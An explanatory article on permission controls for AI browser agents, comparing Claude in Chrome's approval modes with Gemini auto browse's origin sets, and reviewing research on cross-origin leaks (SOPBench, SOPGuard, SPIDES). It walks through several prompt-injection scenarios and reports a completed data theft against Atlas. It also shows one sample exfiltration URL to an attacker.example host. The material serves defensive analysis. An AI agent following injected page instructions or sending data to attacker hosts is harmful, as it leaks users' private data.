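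According to Chromium's security FAQ, an extension with this permission can automate or debug any website. It may also be able to do things on a site that normally require user action in Chrome and so are unavailable to the site's own scripts. In some cases the extension can bypass other restrictions, such as host permissions or the setting for local files. The FAQ gives these abilities as the reason for the permission's broad warning.

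An `activeTab` grant covers one origin in one tab after a click. The debugger API doesn't require a click, and it can connect to embedded frames as well as tabs, according to Chrome for Developers.

Chrome makes only part of the debugger protocol available to extensions, although that part includes the commands for input, pages and network traffic. Chromium's FAQ says the debugger shouldn't let an extension operate Chrome's settings, install other extensions, or run its own code outside the sandbox that separates web pages from the rest of the computer.

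Chromium's developers have tightened the limits on what extensions can debug over time. Chromium's *Do not allow chrome.debugger to attach to web ui pages* (2018) made the browser disconnect the debugger if a tab moves to one of the browser's own pages. Another change that year stopped extensions from debugging local files unless the user has allowed file access. Cronin (2020), in *FYI*, announced that Chrome would decide whether an extension could connect by checking the address of the page that had loaded, which is a better guide to the tab's contents than the address on display.

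These changes protect the browser and the user's files, but they don't confine an extension to certain websites. Chromium's developers discussed that problem in 2014 in *Have the Debugger extension api check that it has access*. One developer had written a check that an extension could access a tab before connecting the debugger to it. A reviewer pointed out that extensions using the debugger had never needed host permissions, so the check would break existing extensions.

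The reviewer suggested an exception for the debugger and thought the team should be able to remove that exception in Manifest V3. The first developer disliked the idea of giving every extension that uses the debugger access to all pages, even though Chrome had already warned the user. But the function they eventually added checks only for restricted addresses, such as Chromium's internal pages.

Manifest V3 has since been released, but the FAQ still includes a warning that the debugger may bypass host permissions. Google's withdrawal of a restriction in Chrome 155 suggests that compatibility is probably still an obstacle.

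The 2014 discussion also mentions a bar that Chrome shows while an extension is debugging a page, unless someone starts Chrome with a switch that hides it. The bar shows that the debugger is connected, but it doesn't include a prompt for the user to approve the site.

### Claude's permission modes

Anthropic's controls are much more detailed than Chrome's. The November 2026 version of Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* describes three modes:

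- **Manually approve:** Claude asks the user before it acts.
- **Automatically approve:** Claude works without stopping at each step, while a safety check reviews every action and blocks those it judges unsafe.
- **Skip all approvals:** Claude doesn't stop to ask, and nothing checks its actions automatically.

The default depends on which side panel the user has. On most paid plans, the panel now runs as a session of Claude Cowork, an Anthropic service that saves the user's tasks to their account. The default there is automatic approval. If an action is blocked, Claude looks for a safer way to do the task or asks the user. After repeated blocks, it goes back to asking about each step.

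Manual approval works differently in the older "classic" panel, which is still available. Claude first writes a plan that lists the websites it expects to use and what it will do there. If the user approves a plan that names their webmail and calendar, Claude can work on both sites without asking about every step, but it has to ask again before using any other site. Zenity Labs found that the extension makes a new plan at the start of each interaction, so an approval lasts for roughly one task.

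In early August 2026, Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* described this plan as the general way manual approval worked. By the end of the month, the guide mentioned the plan only for the classic panel. In the Cowork panel, manual approval means the user answers a prompt before each action.

Claude's approvals therefore last for very different lengths of time:

| What the user approves | How long it lasts |
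|---|---|
| "Allow this time only" in the Cowork panel | One action |
| "Allow all for this website" in the Cowork panel | Probably until revoked |
| A plan in the classic panel | One task |
| "Allow this action" on a site that needs extra approval | One action |
| "Always allow actions on this site" | Until revoked |
| Automatic approval or skipping approvals, as the Cowork panel's mode | Until the user changes the mode |

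Anthropic doesn't say how long "Allow all for this website" lasts. The March version of the extension had only two durations for approving a site, "once" and "always", so a permanent grant seems likely. Users can view and remove approved sites in the extension's settings.

The Cowork panel has no equivalent of the plan, the only one of these approvals that ended with the task. Someone who wants Claude to use their webmail for one task has to approve every action, allow the whole site, or trust the automatic check. Zenity Labs warns that frequent approvals can tire users and tempt them to choose a more permissive mode. Approving a list of sites for each task would take fewer prompts than approving every action, and the access would end with the task.

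Strawberry's *AI permissions* describes a closer match, in which some approvals apply only to a single chat, though Strawberry is an AI browser rather than an extension. These approvals are still broader than Claude's plan because a chat may contain several tasks.

### Actions with stricter rules

Some rules are meant to apply whatever the user has approved. According to Anthropic's November guide, Claude always needs explicit permission to:

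- change permission settings
- grant authorisations, such as letting an app use an account
- enter potentially sensitive information into a website
- delete something permanently, for example by emptying the trash

It also asks before downloading a file, even on a site where the user has chosen "Always allow".

The guide prohibits other actions altogether. Claude may not make purchases, create accounts, trade investments, handle sensitive card or identity data, change system files, or follow instructions in emails or web content. The last rule is harder to enforce than the ban on purchases, because prompt injection works by making such instructions look like the user's.

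Anthropic's pages don't entirely agree about these rules. The guide says that explicit permission is required in every mode, but also that Claude never stops to ask when the user skips approvals. The product page, *Claude in Chrome*, says that purchases "wait for you", which suggests that the user can approve them. The guide lets Claude enter sensitive data with permission, but *Use Claude in Chrome safely* lists this as prohibited.

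Anthropic can also change the rules at any time. At the end of August, Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* still listed permanent deletion as prohibited. By November, Claude could do it with the user's permission. Chrome doesn't ask users to approve such changes, because they add no browser permissions.

Claude's access to a website depends on the site's category. Claude can't open adult sites or sites known for pirated content, and it asks before using financial sites. In the version that sshh12 examined, the extension looked up each site's category on Anthropic's server and cached it for five minutes. This lets Anthropic block a dangerous site without waiting for users to update the extension.

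### What still works when the extension fails

The approval checks are part of the same extension that has the browser's permissions. What remains of each layer depends on what goes wrong:

| What goes wrong | The extension's limits | Chrome's limits |
|---|---|---|
| Text on a page misleads Claude | They still run and may stop the action | They still apply |
| A bug lets a task skip an approval | They fail for that task | They still apply |
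| An attacker publishes a malicious version | The attacker can remove them | They still apply |

Claude's own limits are most useful against misleading text. Chrome can block an extension from a site, but it can't distinguish a click that opens the next message from one that deletes the account. Claude's safety check assesses what the action would do. The extension also confirms that a tab is still on the same domain before it clicks or types, in case the page has changed since Claude chose the action.

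Anthropic reports that its current setup reduces the success rate of attacks to less than 0.08% in tests that combine techniques known to work. This is encouraging, but the tests are Anthropic's own, and they don't measure how Claude would handle a new kind of attack. Anthropic warns that new attacks may succeed and could lead to stolen data.

The approval step has had problems. Zenity Labs saw Claude visit a site that wasn't in its approved plan, and Travis Media's *Claude for Chrome* (2026) relays a report that tasks could start without a real click by the user.

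A takeover like the one at Cyberhaven would be worse, because attackers who published a malicious version of an agent extension could delete the approval step and keep the `debugger` permission. Chrome would install the update without prompting the user, since the update would need no new permissions. Chrome's remaining limits would protect its settings pages, but probably not the user's email or bank account.

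Anthropic also lets companies set lists of allowed and blocked sites for Claude. These lists help against mistakes by the agent or its user, but from sshh12's account, the extension itself appears to enforce them. If so, a malicious version of the extension could ignore them. A company that wants a limit enforced outside the extension could use Chrome's policy for blocked hosts, but would need to test that the policy also stops the debugger on those sites.

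### Claude under Chrome's "on click" setting

Setting Claude in Chrome to "on click" would probably restrict only part of what Claude does, judging from Chromium's code and what sshh12 found, though there doesn't appear to be any published test. A cautious user might choose the setting expecting Claude to wait for them on every site.

Claude reads the text of a page through `scripting`, which depends on site access, so Chrome would block this until the user invoked the extension. But clicks, typing and screenshots go through `debugger`, an API permission. According to a comment in the permissions manager of Chromium (2021), users can't withhold API permissions, so Claude could probably still see the page in a screenshot and click on it.

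Chrome ignores API permissions when it works out whether an extension has access to all sites. Its site access menu could therefore mislead users by showing "on click" for an agent that can already control any page through the debugger API.

It's also unclear whether clicking Claude's icon would restore the missing access, because a toolbar click that opens a side panel doesn't always grant it. Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome troubleshooting* advises users to refresh the page and check that they have granted permission for the site, but this could mean the permission in Chrome's settings or in Claude's.

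A researcher could use a harmless page to test whether the "on click" setting restricts Claude's browser extension. They would choose that setting, approve the page in Claude's own controls, and ask Claude to read the page's text, take a screenshot and click a button. They would repeat the test after clicking the extension's icon, and again after moving to another origin. If the screenshot and the click worked every time, the setting would offer little protection against an agent.

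Even if "on click" restricted everything, it would be awkward for most agents. The delivery-date task needs two sites, so the user would have to click again when Claude moved from the webmail to the calendar. If a task were scheduled for the middle of the night, nobody would be there to click.

### Why the browser should verify the click

When a user clicks an extension's toolbar button, Chrome receives the click in its own interface and can identify the extension and the tab the user was viewing. The extension therefore can't get an `activeTab` grant just by reporting a click.

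Chrome can't verify an approval given in Claude's side panel. Anthropic's code draws the buttons and determines whether the user has agreed. Chrome can't distinguish a button that means "allow this website" from one that means "close". If other software causes the extension to accept a false approval, Chrome can't detect it.

Where a click counts as consent matters more for agents than for other extensions because agents click things themselves. If Chrome treated a click inside a web page as the user's consent, an agent could approve its own requests. Chrome's toolbar is a safer place for approval because the debugger shouldn't be able to operate parts of the browser unrelated to websites.

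Anthropic already uses outside verification for passwords. Claude can ask the password manager 1Password to log in to a site, and the user approves each request with biometrics, such as a fingerprint. 1Password then fills in the password without showing it to Claude. A web page can't supply the fingerprint, so this approval is stronger evidence of consent than a click on a button in the panel. The approval covers only the login, but Claude can act in the account afterwards.

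As with `activeTab`, a verified click doesn't show that the user understood what they were sharing. When a user opens Claude's panel, Claude takes screenshots of the current tab, and the Cowork panel saves the session to the user's history. Anthropic advises users not to open the extension while viewing sensitive information.

Users can start some tasks from Anthropic's desktop app or its coding tool, or schedule them to run every day. These tasks don't begin with a click in Chrome, so the browser has no gesture to verify and would have to rely on a grant the user made earlier. For Claude in Chrome, that grant is the standing access from installation, which contains no information about the task or the sites it needs.

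## How Chrome limits its own agent to the sites a task needs

Google has built its own agent into Chrome, so the browser can control the agent's access separately for each task. The agent is part of Gemini in Chrome, an assistant that runs on Google's Gemini models. Google calls the assistant's ability to carry out tasks on websites "auto browse".

Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, described Google's plan to limit the agent to origins relevant to the user's task. For each task, Chrome would keep one set of origins that the agent may read and another where it may also click and type.

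Google intends these limits to preserve Site Isolation, the Chrome system that separates pages from different websites. An agent with access to every site could undermine that separation if a malicious page misled it.

### From a task to two sets of origins

The design works like this:

1. The user describes a task, such as buying the ingredients for a recipe.
2. A planning model, which decides what the agent does next, proposes an origin.
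3. A gating function decides whether that origin is relevant to the task. It doesn't see the content of web pages.
4. If the gating function approves the origin, Chrome adds it to the read-only set or the read-and-write set.
5. The agent visits the site, and the planning model uses what it finds there to choose the next step.

If the next step needs an origin outside the sets, that origin must first pass a new check. The same applies when a page on its own sends the tab to a new origin.

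Prompt injection is less likely to mislead the gating function than the planning model, which has to read web pages. A hidden instruction might make the planning model propose access to the user's webmail during a shopping task, but the gating function should reject that site as irrelevant.

The user can also share open pages with the agent. The planning model can use their contents, but it still can't add an origin without the gating function's approval. Gemini can also call tools to get information from sources other than web pages. According to Parker, Google separates the calls that read from those that write and checks that both kinds suit the task.

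### What Chrome enforces and what models decide

Deciding which origins are relevant takes judgement, and Google uses a model for at least part of that decision. Once the sets exist, Chrome can enforce them without a model. If a recipe page contains an advertisement in a frame from an unapproved origin, Chrome can leave the frame out of what it sends to the planning model, so an instruction hidden in the advertisement never reaches the model and has no effect.

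Origin sets handle embedded frames more flexibly than `activeTab`, which covers only frames from the top page's origin. A set could include a shop's payment frame and exclude an advertisement on the same page. But it can't filter out hostile text, such as a fake customer review on a product page, if that text shares an origin with useful text.

Under another fixed rule, Chrome restricts web addresses written by the model to known, public ones. An address can carry data, so a misled model could otherwise leak a phone number by opening `https://attacker.example/?phone=5550100`. The rule should exclude addresses made up to contain someone's private details, but it doesn't cover what the agent types into a form.

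Chrome also has some basic checks that don't depend on the task. In an early version of the agent's code, Chromium blocked the agent from acting on:

- unencrypted web pages
- addresses with a numeric IP address instead of a host name
- pages with a pending warning from Safe Browsing, Google's service for detecting dangerous sites
- sites on a block list

If Chromium couldn't check the block list, it refused the action. A later version of Chromium has an option to allow unencrypted pages.

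Google also uses a separate model, which Parker calls the User Alignment Critic, to review each action before the agent performs it. The critic receives information about the proposed action but no unfiltered web content, and it checks only whether the action serves the user's goal. If it rejects the action, the planning model receives feedback and tries another plan. After repeated failures, the planning model can return control to the user.

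The critic can stop harmful actions on permitted sites, which the origin sets can't do. For example, it could reject an attempt to delete the user's account at a shop where the agent is supposed to buy something. But it has less context than the planning model. A page might also influence the critic indirectly, because the planning model reads the page before proposing an action. Parker claims only that web content can't poison the critic directly.

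While the agent is active, another model checks every page for prompt injection. Parker acknowledges it can't catch everything and gives no figures for how often attacks get through these defences. Google offers researchers up to $20,000 for demonstrating serious breaches.

### What Google has released

The first release had only the read-and-write set. Parker said that Google couldn't easily find the right balance before seeing how the limits affected people's tasks.

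Some non-business users got auto browse in Chrome 144, according to Google's *Chrome Enterprise and Education release notes*. In March, *The New Era of Browsing* (Rafa, 2026) described it as a preview for subscribers to Google's Pro and Ultra plans. In April, Google let eligible business customers turn it on, initially in the United States, according to TechWyse's *Google Brings Gemini-Powered Auto Browse and Shadow IT Detection to Chrome Enterprise*. In August, *Gemini in Chrome for Android is rolling out to everyone* (Payne, 2026) reported that it was reaching Android users in the United States.

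There is no public sign that Google has added the read-only set. In *Future Mode Part 2*, Berschadski (August 2026) wrote that Chrome limits the agent to origins strictly relevant to its task, but he didn't mention separate sets. In Chromium (2025), the code that coordinates the agent's tasks refers to "writable" origins but has no equivalent for read-only ones.

This code also shows how Chrome handles a tab that is about to move to another page:

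1. If the new page has the same origin, Chrome allows it.
2. If the address is on a block list from Google or the user's company, Chrome blocks it.
3. If the address is on an allowed list from either of them, Chrome allows it.
4. Otherwise, Chrome needs a further check, which can include asking Google's server to accept or reject the new origin.

At least some of the relevance checks therefore seem to happen on Google's server, and the browser enforces the answer.

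It's unclear how many users have this server check. Chromium's default settings turn on the general control on moving between origins but leave the server check for new origins off, and Google can change these settings for groups of users. Comments in Chromium's code also describe a "dark launch" mode, in which Chrome asks the server about a new origin but records the answer without acting on it. This would let Google measure how often the check would block a task before enforcing it.

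By default, Chrome also adds a site to the agent's allowed origins when the agent asks to open it. In an automated Chromium test that refuses every request for confirmation, the agent can still open a new site directly and then follow a link to it. Chrome blocks that link once a new task begins, so the permission ends with the task. However, this browser check doesn't stop the agent from opening a site it chose itself. Parker wrote that such a site has to pass a relevance check first, so Google may run that check on its server before sending the instruction to Chrome.

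The code can also hide frames from other websites in screenshots, but this option is part of a screenshot method that is off by default. Which frames it hides depends on whether they come from the top page's site, not on whether the task needs them.

Companies can set their own limits. Google's *Gemini in Chrome*, a guide for administrators, lists one policy that controls auto browse and two that set allowed and blocked addresses. Chrome enforces these lists itself, whereas Claude's extension appears to enforce the lists that companies set for Claude. The guide also states that auto browse isn't available to managed users, but this conflicts with the April announcement and is probably out of date.

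### When the agent stops for the user

Before a task begins, the user reviews a plan and clicks "Start Task", according to Google's *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse*. The agent is also supposed to stop at certain points during the task:

| What the agent is about to do | What the user does | What triggers the stop |
|---|---|---|
| Open a sensitive site, such as a bank or medical site | Confirms the visit | A fixed list of sites |
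| Sign in with a saved password | Gives permission | The request to Google Password Manager |
| Complete a purchase | Confirms it or completes the final step | The agent's checks on sensitive actions |
| Send a message | Confirms it or sends it personally | The agent's checks on sensitive actions |

The first two stops are more reliable because Chrome can recognise a listed site or a request for a password. The other two depend partly on software correctly predicting what a button will do. Google warns that Gemini might complete a purchase without permission, and it holds users responsible for the result.

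Berschadski makes the stronger claim that Chrome requires human approval before any high-stakes action. Google's help page is probably the better guide, since it says only that Gemini "aims to ask". Its other examples of when Gemini should ask include submitting forms and changing the user's data. Gemini may ask the user to take over to create an account or accept terms of service.

Permission to sign in can last longer than a task. Google Password Manager keeps a list of sites where the user has let Gemini sign in automatically, and the user can remove sites from it. Even with this permission, the agent in Parker's design would still need the site in its origin set before it could act there.

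### A shopping task across two sites

Suppose a user asks Gemini to find a lentil soup recipe on `https://recipes.example.com` and put the ingredients in their basket at `https://grocer.example.org`. Under the full design, starting from an empty tab, the sets might change like this:

| Step | Read-only set | Read-and-write set |
|---|---|---|
| The user starts the task. | Empty | Empty |
| The gating function approves the recipe site for reading. | `recipes.example.com` | Empty |
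| The agent reads the ingredients. Chrome leaves out an advertisement from another origin. | `recipes.example.com` | Empty |
| The gating function approves the grocer for reading and acting. | `recipes.example.com` | `grocer.example.org` |
| The agent adds the ingredients to the basket. | `recipes.example.com` | `grocer.example.org` |
| A fake review on the grocer's site tells the agent to open the user's webmail. The gating function rejects the webmail site. | `recipes.example.com` | `grocer.example.org` |
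| The user takes over and pays. | `recipes.example.com` | `grocer.example.org` |
| The task ends. | Empty | Empty |

The agent can give the grocer the list of ingredients, but it can't post a comment on the recipe site. In the first release, the recipe site would probably have been in the read-and-write set too, so only the critic or a confirmation could have stopped the comment.

The fake review could instead tell the agent to buy 20 bags of lentils. The origin sets wouldn't prevent this, because the agent is already allowed to act on the grocer's site. The critic might approve the purchase, since lentils fit the task and the critic can't read the recipe page. The user would have to notice the quantity before paying.

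The limits on the agent don't apply to the user. In Chromium's tests, a link to a blocked site works once the user has taken over. So if the grocer sends customers to a separate payment site that the agent can't open, the user can still pay there.

The example also shows that the agent has to carry some data from one site to another, which creates a risk even with origin sets. *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* tested seven agentic browsers and found that a malicious site could exploit the least restrictive ones to steal data from other origins.

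### How origin sets differ from activeTab

| | `activeTab` | Chrome's agent |
|---|---|---|
| Who starts the grant | The user, by invoking the extension | The user starts the task, and the planning model then proposes origins |
| Who chooses the scope | The user chooses the page, and Chrome grants access to its origin | The gating function, within the limits of Google's and the company's lists |
| What ends it | The tab moves to another origin or closes, or the user disables the extension | The task ends or the user stops it |
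| What the user sees | The page on which they invoked the extension | A plan, an icon on the tab and a log of the agent's steps |

The origin sets suit the shopping task better because the agent can go back to the recipe without losing access to the grocer. With `activeTab`, the user would have to click again each time the agent moved between the sites, but would know exactly which sites they had chosen.

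Chrome's browsing history marks the sites the auto browse agent visited, and its log shows each step as it happens. Both help users notice a mistake, but someone who isn't watching may notice it only after the agent has shared their data.

### Letting a model choose the sites

With auto browse, Gemini chooses which sites to use and may share the user's personal information with them. Google tells users this when it asks them to review the plan. In Claude's classic panel, by contrast, the user approves a plan that names the sites.

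There are good reasons to let a model choose the sites. Someone may ask an agent to find a cheap hotel partly because they don't know which sites have the best prices. They also may not recognise the separate addresses a hotel uses for bookings or payments. If Chrome asked about every origin, people might start approving requests without reading them, as Roesner and colleagues warned about frequent prompts. A gating function can apply the same check to every origin, however many there are.

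The main objection to this design is that the gating function can only predict what the user would want. If a user asks Gemini to sort out their travel expenses, the function could reasonably approve access to their webmail, their bank and their employer's systems, though the user may have meant only a folder of receipts. A fraudulent shop is also relevant to a shopping task, so a relevance check may let it through.

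Google also has to keep the gating function from interrupting too many tasks. Parker wrote that Google would adjust it to reduce unnecessary friction while improving security, but those aims can conflict, because a looser check lets more tasks finish but also lets a misled agent reach more sites.

The case for letting a model choose is strongest for public pages that the agent only needs to read, and weaker for sites where the user is logged in or that would receive personal details. Chrome's confirmation for sensitive sites covers some of these. Parker gives banking and medical sites as examples but doesn't mention webmail, which can also contain bank statements and medical letters.

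Chromium's code includes a setting, off by default, that makes Chrome prompt the user about new origins instead of relying on Google's server.

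## Data that an agent carries between permitted sites

A list of permitted sites controls where an agent can go, but not what it takes from one site to another. To copy a delivery date from the user's webmail into their calendar, for example, an agent needs access to both. It reads the email, keeps the text in its working history and types the date into the calendar. With the same access, it could also paste the whole email into an event that the user's colleagues can see.

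`activeTab` and Chrome's origin sets limit access, meaning which sites an agent can read or act on. Limits on data flow restrict where the agent may send what it has read. A read-only origin set does some of this too, because it keeps the agent from writing data to the sites in it.

Browsers have mostly let users decide what data to carry between sites. The same-origin policy restricts scripts, but a person can copy text from one tab and paste it into another. When an agent does the copying, the user may not know that any data has moved.

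### Agents as confused deputies

In computer security, a confused deputy is a program that an outsider tricks into using its legitimate access on the outsider's behalf. Suppose a user asks an agent to check their webmail and then answer a comment on a forum. An attacker on the forum can't open the user's mailbox, but a prompt injection in the attacker's comment could make the agent paste an email into its reply, where the attacker can read it.

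A correct list of sites wouldn't prevent this leak, because the agent needs both the webmail and the forum to do what the user asked. To stop it, the browser would also have to track where the text came from or whose instructions the agent was following.

### Tests of seven agentic browsers

In April 2026, Franziska Roesner and David Kohlbrenner of the University of Washington presented *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, which examines how easily this could happen. They ran their tests in late January and early February on the versions available then.

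The researchers built harmless web pages about a person called Alice. One page said she liked cats, and a frame embedded in it from another origin said she liked horses. They asked each agent which animals Alice liked, and an answer that included horses showed the agent had read the frame. They also checked whether the agent would type into a page, and whether it would follow instructions written on a page when the user told it to.

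| Product | Read a frame from another origin | Typed text at the user's request | Followed the page's instructions |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Atlas in Agent Mode | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | Yes, with auto browse | No |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | Yes | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | Yes, except passwords | No |
| Brave Leo AI, Edge with Copilot, Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |

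The researchers completed a data theft only on Atlas, OpenAI's browser. Their test page contained a frame from another origin and an instruction to the agent. When the user asked for a summary, Atlas included the frame's text in its summary and typed the summary into a form, which automatically sent it to the attacker's server.

The attack also worked in the other direction, with a frame taking text from the page around it. This version is more worrying because a malicious advertisement on a webmail page could use it. In the first version, the attacker has to embed the sensitive site in their own page, and many sites block embedding or don't show private data when embedded.

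In Gemini, Claude and Comet, the researchers found the preconditions for the same theft. The agent could already read one origin and write to another, so the products relied on the model to refuse. The researchers tried only a simple prompt injection, which didn't work, and inventing better ones wasn't their aim. The results therefore don't show that an attacker could have stolen data from these products.

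Copilot read tabs from different origins without asking, but it couldn't have leaked their contents in this way because it couldn't type into a page.

Some agents also kept information after the user had left a site. Near the end of the tests, Comet listed animals it had gathered from past conversations and from pages the researchers had visited. An agent with this kind of memory can carry data from a site after its access to that site has ended. It can also carry false data, such as a phone number from a fake banking site that the agent might later repeat as the bank's real one.

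### The companies' responses

Brave, Google and Microsoft acknowledged the findings. OpenAI declined the report because the researchers didn't have an end-to-end prompt injection attack. Anthropic, Firefox and Perplexity hadn't replied when the paper came out. According to a later University of Washington article, Perplexity also declined the report, and Anthropic and Firefox still hadn't responded.

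The paper and the article report no fixes by any of the companies, and according to the article, there is no clear way to solve the problems while keeping the browsers' capabilities. Gemini read a frame from another origin in these tests, so Chrome evidently didn't apply its rule about unapproved frames to an ordinary question about a page.

OpenAI has since dropped Atlas. BGR's *OpenAI Has Already Discontinued Its Controversial ChatGPT Atlas Browser* (2026) gives 9 August 2026 as the planned end date and reports commercial reasons, mainly that it is hard to persuade people to change browsers. The Indian Express' *OpenAI to shut down ChatGPT Atlas browser* lists three replacements: a Chrome extension, a browser inside the ChatGPT desktop app and a browser that runs on OpenAI's servers. The university's tests covered none of these, so they don't show whether the replacements have the same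 weakness as Atlas.

### How often agents leak data in SOPBench

The Washington tests showed that a leak was possible but not how often one would happen. The security firm Trail of Bits had also demonstrated data theft in agentic browsers, which it did not name, in *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026). The firm recommended extending the same-origin policy to AI agents.

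In *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) measured the leaks and built a defence along those lines. Their benchmark, SOPBench, uses ten categories of source site that hold private data: shopping, banking, airlines, email, calendars, messages, recruitment, documents, insurance and pharmacies. The five destination sites are X, Discord, GitHub, Reddit and Google Forms. Most of the pages are imitations, so no real data was at risk.

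In a typical run, the user asks the agent to do something with private data on the source site and then do an unrelated job at the destination, such as replying to a post. The attacker has placed instructions there for the agent to include the private data. The researchers counted a leak only if the agent wrote the exact data the attacker wanted, not a loose paraphrase.

They tested five agentic browsers with six models between them. The open-source browsers went through 100 runs for each pair of source and destination. Comet and Atlas went through only three, because someone had to operate them by hand. These are the results for banking data with attack text that the researchers wrote themselves:

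| Browser and model | X | Discord | GitHub | Reddit | Google Forms |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| VisualWebArena, GPT-5.4 | 47% | 90% | 47% | 59% | 43% |
| SeeAct, GPT-5.4 | 100% | 100% | 97% | 86% | 93% |
| BrowserOS, GPT-5.4 | 70% | 41% | 78% | 27% | 100% |
| Comet, Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 3 of 3 | 1 of 3 | 2 of 3 | 2 of 3 | 2 of 3 |
| Atlas, GPT-5.5 | 1 of 3 | 1 of 3 | 2 of 3 | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

Three runs are too few to give a reliable rate for any one pair. Across all 50 pairs, the overall rate was about two thirds for Atlas and between 60% and 67% for Comet, depending on the model. Google Forms produced some of the highest rates, probably because the attacker controls the whole form and the agent's task is to fill it in.

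The rates rose when another AI model refined the attack text over several attempts. In BrowserOS with GPT-5.4, for example, the leak rate for banking data sent to Reddit went from 27% to 65%.

Without an attacker, the researchers saw no leaks when the agent visited the two sites one after the other. When the source page was in a frame inside the destination page, however, BrowserOS leaked data in every run. In those runs, the user had asked the agent to do something like summarise the whole page and write the summary into a text box. The agent did what the user literally asked, so the 100% rate mostly shows that this request is dangerous on a page with content from different origins.

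Detecting the attacker's text doesn't look like a reliable alternative to controlling the data. Wang and colleagues tried five detectors, and none kept both missed attacks and false alarms low. WebSentinel, for example, missed almost no attacks but flagged between 6% and 44% of harmless pages, depending on the site.

### How SOPGuard tracks where data came from

SOPGuard, the researchers' defence, adds a check on data flow to BrowserOS. It works in four steps:

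1. When the agent reads a page, SOPGuard saves the text with a label that gives the page's origin.
2. When the agent produces new text, SOPGuard asks the agent's model which saved items the text draws on. The new text inherits all their labels.
3. When the agent is about to write into a page, SOPGuard compares the text's labels with that page's origin.
4. If any label differs, SOPGuard pauses the action and asks the user to approve or deny it.

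Suppose an agent reads a balance of $2,000 on `https://bank.example.com` and a rent bill of $1,200 in an email on `https://mail.example.com`. It works out that $800 will be left and wants to enter this in a budget at `https://sheets.example.org`:

```
labels("$2,000") = {bank}
labels("$1,200") = {mail}
labels("$800")   = {bank} ∪ {mail} = {bank, mail}
destination      = sheets
```

Neither label matches the spreadsheet site, so SOPGuard prompts the user. If the agent wrote the result into an email draft instead, SOPGuard would still prompt the user because only the `mail` label would match.

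SOPGuard reduced the violation rate in SOPBench to 0.00, both with and without an attacker. Tasks took 2.07% to 5.79% longer. In one comparison with GPT-5.4, the average time rose from 34.4 to 36.3 seconds. The researchers found no significant change in how many tasks the agent completed. The extra questions to the model cost money, and the researchers list reducing that cost as future work.

Wang and colleagues don't count a transfer as a violation if the user approves it, so the 0.00 figure shows that SOPGuard caught the transfers in the benchmark, but not that people would refuse the harmful ones.

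### How often SOPGuard would interrupt people

By design, SOPGuard should ask the user whenever a legitimate task moves text between sites. It records where data came from but not whether the data is private. If a user asks an agent to copy laptop specifications from several shops into an online notebook, SOPGuard treats those public specifications as it would a bank balance and asks before the agent saves them.

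Wang and colleagues' main evaluation measures completed tasks and running time but doesn't count approval prompts. Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) counted them in *SPIDES* while testing a rival defence. They built 28 linked websites and gave agents 56 harmless tasks, 22 of which required moving data between origins. SOPGuard requested 0.22 approvals per completed task, or about one for every four or five.

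That average is tolerable, but it seems low. If SOPGuard had prompted the user at least once in each of the 22 cross-site tasks, and agents had completed all 56 tasks, the average would have been at least 0.39. Either some data moved without a prompt or agents completed fewer of the cross-site tasks. The average also depends on the mix of tasks, so someone who mostly uses an agent to move information between sites would see many more prompts.

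Zverev and colleagues assumed an ideal user who always distinguishes safe requests from unsafe ones. Real users are less reliable, especially when prompts are frequent. SOPGuard's prompt names the origins involved, but to make an informed choice about a transfer from webmail to a calendar, the user also needs to see whether the agent is sending a date or the whole email.

### Whether labels survive paraphrase

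SOPGuard asks the model where the meaning of the data came from, because a search for copied text would miss anything the agent had summarised. In the budget example, "$800" appears on neither source page, but the model can still trace it to both.

The simplest alternative would be to label everything the agent writes with every site it has visited. This would never miss a source, but once the agent had visited a few sites, almost every action would trigger a prompt. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes this as label explosion, in which every piece of data ends up with every label and the labels become useless.

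Wang and colleagues tested the model's labels on data from two to ten origins. In each case, the agent had to produce three new results in a row, and later ones could build on earlier ones. People worked out the correct labels, and the researchers scored the overlap:

```
score = labels in both sets / labels in either set
```

If the correct labels were `bank` and `mail` and the model gave only `bank`, the score would be 1/2. GPT-5.4 and OpenAI o3 averaged at least 0.955 at every number of origins. GPT-5.4-mini stayed above 0.9 with up to eight origins but did worse than the other two, so the method may not suit weaker models.

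Many labelling mistakes are harmless. If the model omitted the `mail` label on the $800, SOPGuard would still prompt the user before the agent wrote it into the spreadsheet, because the remaining `bank` label doesn't match the spreadsheet's site either. A mistake allows a leak only if no label from another site remains.

An attacker could try to cause that mistake, because the model that assigns the labels also reads the attacker's page. The attacker might write there that the page is the only source of the text. The researchers tried this on 100 cases. Their own attack text had almost no effect, and text refined by another model raised the violation rate only slightly, after many more attempts. That is a good result, but a defence that relies on a model's judgement can't guarantee a violation rate of 0.00 against a better attack.

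### Leaks that origin labels miss

Data can also leak within one site. If an agent takes the address a user has saved with a shop and posts it in a public review on that shop's site, the labels match, so SOPGuard doesn't prompt the user. Zverev and colleagues argue from such cases that checking origins isn't enough. They also argue that it isn't always necessary, because some cross-site tasks are legitimate.

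In their tests, between 53.2% and 73.2% of attacks succeeded against SOPGuard, depending on the model. This doesn't contradict Wang and colleagues' result of 0.00, because half of the 56 attacks tried to make the agent take an unauthorised action, such as placing an order, which SOPGuard wasn't built to stop. The researchers also assumed the worst case, in which the attacker controls the model's output as soon as the model reads hostile text.

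Their own system, SPIDES, relies on websites to label parts of a page. For example, a shop can mark its reviews as untrusted and a saved address as private. SPIDES replaces this text with placeholders until the agent needs it, and fixed rules then determine which actions require approval. No attack succeeded, and agents completed between 67.1% and 86.1% of the harmless tasks. But SPIDES required 1.84 approvals per completed task, over eight times as many as SOPGuard, and it works only if websites label their pages correctly.

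An agent can reveal private data without writing it. *AgentTell* (Shahriar, Rahman and colleagues, 2026) tested agents that learned a private fact on one site and then completed a task on another, after the user had told them not to share personal details. In one example, the agent learns that the user belongs to a trade union and then registers the user for an event, either through the union or without naming any organisation. Agents that knew about the membership chose the union in 90.3% of sessions, which revealed the membership to the event's website.

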